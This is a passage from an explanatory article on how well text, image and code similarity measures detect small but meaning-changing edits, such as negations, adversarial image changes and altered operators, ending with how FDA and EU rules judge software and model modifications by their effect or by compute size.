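| Two-way entailment | 0.395 | 0.670 |

The difference in length, a crude measure of change size, predicted the ratings better than any embedding, BERTScore or entailment method. The students took off a point for each error, and the most common error was leaving something out, which usually shortens a clause. So size helped to assess ordinary simplifications, but it was almost no help in detecting an edit that reversed the law. A developer who chose the score that best matched these ratings would choose length over entailment.

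### Can the scores tell reversals from paraphrases?

In *How Small Transformation Expose the Weakness of Semantic Similarity Measures*, Nikiema, Djiré and colleagues (2025) tested 18 similarity measures on edits that change meaning and edits that keep it. For the text part, they took short descriptions of programming tasks from the question-and-answer site Stack Overflow and made versions with synonyms, in French, with a negation added or removed, and with a word replaced by its opposite. The table shows average scores, where 1 means the same meaning.

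| Method | Synonyms | French | Negation | Opposite word |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| BERTScore | 0.92 | 0.85 | 0.95 | 0.95 |
| MPNet embeddings | 0.83 | 0.65 | 0.88 | 0.77 |
| OpenAI embeddings | 0.79 | 0.80 | 0.78 | 0.72 |
| GPT-4o as judge | 0.72 | 0.62 | 0.29 | 0.25 |
| DeepSeek-V3 as judge | 0.87 | 0.83 | 0.23 | 0.35 |

BERTScore gave both kinds of reversal a higher average than either kind of rewording. A threshold low enough to accept a typical synonym version would therefore accept a typical reversal too. Even unrelated texts averaged 0.82. The OpenAI embeddings scored the rewordings slightly higher than the reversals, but the gaps are too small to be much use.

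The two judges separated the groups clearly on average, but the averages don't show how often a judge would get an individual pair wrong. Some labels may also be wrong, because the program that chose the synonyms may sometimes have changed the meaning.

Asking the judges to reason step by step made them more lenient. GPT-4o's average score for pairs with different meanings rose from 0.19 with a simple prompt to 0.40, and its scores for synonyms and translations also rose. Anyone using a judge with a fixed pass mark would need to recheck that mark after changing the prompt.

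### Training a measure to respond to "not"

If a score ignores negation, developers can train it on examples of negation. Anschütz, Lozano and Groh (2023), in *This is not correct! Negation-aware Evaluation of Language Generation Systems*, did this with BLEURT, which uses a language model to predict how highly a person would rate a sentence as a version of a reference sentence. One version of BLEURT had given 0.67 to a sentence that contradicted the reference.

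The researchers collected 68,780 pairs of sentences, half of them negations or other contradictions and half paraphrases. To make some of the negations, they wrote a program that finds a sentence's main verb and adds or removes "not". They labelled the contradictions 0 and the paraphrases 1, and added human ratings of machine translations so that the measure would keep responding to other errors. They trained a small version of BLEURT on this mixture to make NegBLEURT, and trained an embedding model, MPNet, on the negation data to make NegMPNet.

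The next table shows how much different errors lowered the scores in a standard test of translation measures. A higher number means a larger fall.

| Error | BLEURT-20 | NegBLEURT | MPNet | NegMPNet |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Negation | 0.15 | 0.93 | 0.14 | 0.65 |
| Opposite word | 0.09 | 0.38 | 0.07 | 0.24 |
| Replaced name | 0.20 | 0.38 | 0.12 | 0.04 |
| Changed number | 0.05 | 0.09 | 0.01 | 0.02 |
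| Changed gender | 0.10 | 0.02 | 0.01 | 0.01 |
| Misspelling | 0.06 | 0.28 | 0.03 | 0.03 |
| Unrelated sentence | 0.81 | 1.64 | 0.98 | 1.03 |

NegBLEURT's training worked for negation and helped with opposites, which were also in the training data, but it did little for changed numbers. The metric's score fell three times as far for a misspelling as for a wrong number, although a wrong number in a prescription is usually far more dangerous.

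The MPNet columns give the fairer comparison because they show the same model before and after training, whereas BLEURT-20 is a different version from the small one that became NegBLEURT. But NegMPNet became less sensitive to replaced names, and its score on a set of search tasks fell from 43.1 to 36.1. Anschütz and colleagues fixed the fault they targeted, but someone who needs a measure to catch wrong doses or swapped names would have to train and test it for those too.

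### How different do two pictures look?

SSIM, short for structural similarity, compares two pictures one small window at a time. For windows x and y, the score is

((2μₓμᵧ + c₁)(2σₓᵧ + c₂)) / ((μₓ² + μᵧ² + c₁)(σₓ² + σᵧ² + c₂))

Here μ is a window's average brightness, σ² measures how much its pixels vary, and σₓᵧ measures how closely the two windows vary together. The small constants c₁ and c₂ prevent division by numbers near zero. The final score is the average over all windows, and identical pictures score 1.

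Brightening a window evenly doesn't change its pattern, so only the brightness part of the score falls. If the average brightness rises from 0.5 to 0.8, SSIM is about 0.8 / 0.89, or 0.90. Scrambling the pixels within the window would preserve the average brightness but destroy the pattern, so SSIM would fall much further.

LPIPS uses a neural network trained to recognise objects. It runs both pictures through the network, records the numbers that several layers compute, rescales them and measures how far apart the two sets are. With φ(x) for the rescaled numbers, one version is

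LPIPS(x, x′) = ‖φ(x) − φ(x′)‖₂

This is the L2 norm again, but it measures a difference between the network's internal numbers instead of between pixels.

Laidlaw, Singla and Feizi (2020), in *Perceptual Adversarial Robustness*, asked people how noticeable 14 types of adversarial change were. People's judgments had a correlation of 0.58 with L2 distance between pixels and 0.68 with SSIM. The correlation with LPIPS was 0.81 to 0.85 when its network was trained normally, but 0.61 to 0.70 when it was trained adversarially.

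LPIPS also worked better than L2 as a limit for training. A classifier trained to resist changes within an LPIPS limit was right 68% of the time under an attack that slightly warps the picture, and 73% under one that alters its colours. A classifier trained with an L2 limit was right 15% and 60% of the time. Training against each attack specifically did best, at 76% and 81%, but developers can only do that for attacks they already know about.

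A score that matches how people see pictures can still be a poor predictor of what a model will do. In *Vision-Language Model Confidence Is Not a Property of the Answer*, an attack altered pictures to make a model more confident in its wrong answers and less confident in its right ones. The altered pictures had a distance of 0.067 from the originals on LPIPS, a score of how different two pictures look to people. Harmlessly cropping a picture by two pixels and resizing it gave a larger distance, 0.074. An LPIPS limit that allows the crop would also allow the attack.

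### Asking people directly

The most direct way to find out whether people notice a change is to ask them. *SCOOTER* (Fazlija, Zühlke and colleagues, 2025) tested six attacks that aren't limited by pixel norms. Three change the colours in a picture, and three use diffusion models, a type of image generator. The attacks are supposed to produce pictures that look untouched.

Fazlija and colleagues had 346 people rate real and attacked pictures by how modified they looked. To pass, an attack's pictures had to average within 0.2 points of the real ones. All six attacks failed. GPT-4o consistently flagged the attacked pictures for four of the six, so the researchers suggest using it as a first screen before paying for a human study. They also note that many earlier papers relied on automatic scores that predict human perception poorly, or didn't check at all.

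Human studies need careful design. Participants first had to pass a colour-blindness test, because people who can't see a colour change would make an attack look better than it is. They then had to pass a check that they understood the task. A session takes about 18 minutes and costs about £2.70 per person at the researchers' example rate of £9 an hour. This is affordable for a study, but too slow and expensive for checking every picture a system receives.

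The question people are asked also matters. If someone skilfully changes a speed limit sign in a photograph from 30 to 80, the picture may look completely natural, and people asked whether it looks modified would then say no. To find the change in meaning, a researcher has to ask what the speed limit is.

### Comparing programs by their text

Measures that compare the text of programs also handle small harmful edits poorly. For the code part of their study, Nikiema and colleagues took 561 programs that passed their tests and made two versions of each. One version had harmless edits, such as renamed variables, and the other had changes to operators or to the order in which instructions run. They reran the tests to confirm that the first version still worked and that the second behaved differently. They also compared pairs of working solutions to the same problem, one simple and one complicated.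 The table shows average similarity scores.

| Method | Harmless edits | Another working solution | Altered behaviour |
|---|---|---|---|
| CodeBERT embeddings | 1.00 | 0.98 | 1.00 |
| OpenAI embeddings | 0.82 | 0.54 | 0.87 |
| GPT-4o as judge | 0.97 | 0.63 | 0.62 |
| DeepSeek-V3 as judge | 0.97 | 0.71 | 0.78 |

The judges did worse on programs than on ordinary text. GPT-4o scored altered programs about the same as working alternative solutions, and DeepSeek-V3 scored the altered programs higher. Both models are old, and current ones can probably follow a program's logic much better.

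Nikiema and colleagues report that CodeBERT's results improved by 24–66% when they used straight-line distance instead of cosine similarity, but the switch mainly lowered all the scores. The average fell from 0.999 to 0.758 for altered programs and from 0.998 to 0.688 for harmlessly edited ones, so the altered programs still scored as more similar to the originals.

Two versions of a program share most of their text, which is part of the problem. *Excision Score* (Gruzinov, Sycheva and colleagues, 2025) describes a measure that removes the shared text before comparing. It needs the original, a known correct revision and the revision to be scored.

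Suppose the dose function has `<` by mistake. The correct revision changes it to `>`, but a model changes it to `==`. The model's version matches 21 of the correct version's 22 tokens, or 95%, but if you compare only the part that changed, nothing matches. On a set of code repairs, the correlation between this second measure and test results was 12% higher than for the next best measure. It still needs a correct answer to compare with, though, and a correct repair written differently can score badly.

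### Running the program

Tests measure behaviour more directly, but only for the inputs someone chose. Gruzinov and colleagues add that tests need code that can run, which rules out fragments and incomplete projects. They also note that tests can be slow, citing one team that took two days to evaluate about 300 programming tasks, including the time the model spent writing its answers. Another team took an hour for 500 tasks, using powerful hardware and an optimised setup.

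An equivalence checker covers every input to the functions it can handle. For the dose function, the next table compares a checker that can handle it with the two earlier tests, which use doses of 5 and 50 with a limit of 10.

| Edit | Token edits | Tests | Equivalence checker | Effect |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `>` to `<` | 1 | Fail | Different | Approves overdoses |
| `>` to `>=` | 1 | Pass | Different | Rejects a dose exactly at the limit |
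| Added check for a missing dose | 7 | Pass | Different | Rejects a list with a missing dose |
| Complete rewrite | 15 | Pass | Same | None |

The tests miss the change to `>=`, but the equivalence checker finds it. The checker can show that behaviour changed but not whether the change was an improvement, so it gives the same result for an edit that approves overdoses and one that catches missing doses. Every successful bug fix also fails an equivalence check, because its purpose is to change what the program does.

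An equivalence checker is the better choice for refactoring, where the program's behaviour shouldn't change. For a repair or a new feature, developers need tests of the new behaviour, though they can sometimes use a checker on the parts that should stay the same. Both methods can miss harm that the program's outputs don't show, such as a slowdown that makes the program too slow to use in an emergency.

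### An official rule based on effects

Regulators also have to decide which changes deserve attention. In the United States, many medical devices need clearance from the Food and Drug Administration (FDA), through an application called a 510(k), before they go on sale. The FDA's *Deciding When to Submit a 510(k) for a Software Change* (2017) advises manufacturers on when a software change to a cleared device needs a new application. The FDA still listed it as final guidance in June 2026.

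The main test is whether the change could significantly affect the device's safety or effectiveness, for better or worse. Changes that only strengthen cybersecurity or bring the device back to its approved specification usually need no new application. For other changes, the manufacturer asks whether the change creates a risk of serious harm that the device doesn't already control, whether it changes a safeguard against such harm, and whether it could significantly affect how well the device does its medical job. The table shows the outcomes for some of the FDA's examples.

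| Change | New application? |
|---|---|
| New company logo on every screen, involving many parts of the software | Probably not |
| Barcode reader corrected to handle an invalid character as specified | Probably not |
| Surgical robot allowed to move further before its safety stop | Yes |
| Core algorithm completely rewritten, with the same claimed performance | Possibly |

Changing the logo may involve far more code than changing the robot's safety threshold, but only the threshold affects a patient. Although the robot's manufacturer had concluded that the wider limit was still safe, the change needed a new application because it altered a safeguard against serious injury.

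In the guidance, the FDA still treats size as a warning sign. A complete rewrite may unintentionally affect performance, so the FDA says it may need review even if the manufacturer expects no difference. A change that could significantly affect safety still needs an application even if it passes testing. Because minor changes can add up, manufacturers have to compare each new version with the last one the FDA cleared, rather than the one just before it.

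This approach depends on the manufacturer's judgment. The FDA acknowledges that it has sometimes disagreed with manufacturers about what counts as "significant". It also notes that people often can't estimate how likely a software failure is, in which case they should judge the risk by how severe the harm would be.

### An official rule based on size

The European Commission's *Guidelines on the scope of obligations for providers of general-purpose AI models* (2025) use size to answer a different question: whether a company that modifies another company's general-purpose model becomes a provider too. Under the EU's AI Act, the provider of such a model has duties such as documenting how it was trained.

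The European Commission (2025) says that a company that modifies a model becomes a provider if the modification significantly changes the model's generality, capabilities or systemic risk, meaning the risk of large-scale harm from the most capable models. Because this is hard to judge directly, the guidelines use computing power as a substitute, measured as the total number of arithmetic operations (FLOP). A company normally becomes a provider if its modification uses more than a third of the computing power used to train the original model. For a model trained with 3 × 10²⁵ FLOP, the threshold is 10²⁵ FLOP.

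If a company doesn't know and can't estimate how much computing power was used to train the original model, the threshold is a third of 10²⁵ FLOP for models classed as having systemic risk and a third of 10²³ FLOP for others. The threshold is normally relative to the original model's training compute because training a larger model on the same data takes more computing power. A fixed number would treat the same modification differently depending on the model's size.

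The European Commission's *General FAQ* explains that the high threshold is meant to keep a provider's duties from falling on most companies that adapt existing models. Companies that cross it must document only their own modification and the data they used. But if the original model has systemic risk, the modifier must also assess and reduce the risks of the new version. The guidelines aren't legally binding, and each case still needs its own assessment, but the Commission bases its enforcement on them.

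The threshold would be a poor test of whether a modified model is safe. Suppose the original was trained on 15 trillion tokens. The computing power used in training grows roughly in proportion to the amount of data, so a company would need to train the model on about 5 trillion more tokens to reach the threshold. Training on 10 million tokens would use about 500,000 times less computing power, but it could do great harm if it taught the model to give dangerous instructions that it used to refuse.

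The European Commission wants a rule that companies can apply cheaply and predictably, so it bases its threshold on computing power, which they can estimate before training starts. It doesn't claim that modifications below the threshold are safe. It expects few modifications to cross the threshold at present, and says it may change its approach as the technology and the market develop. The FDA wants to review risky changes before they reach patients, so it accepts a rule that takes more expertise to apply.
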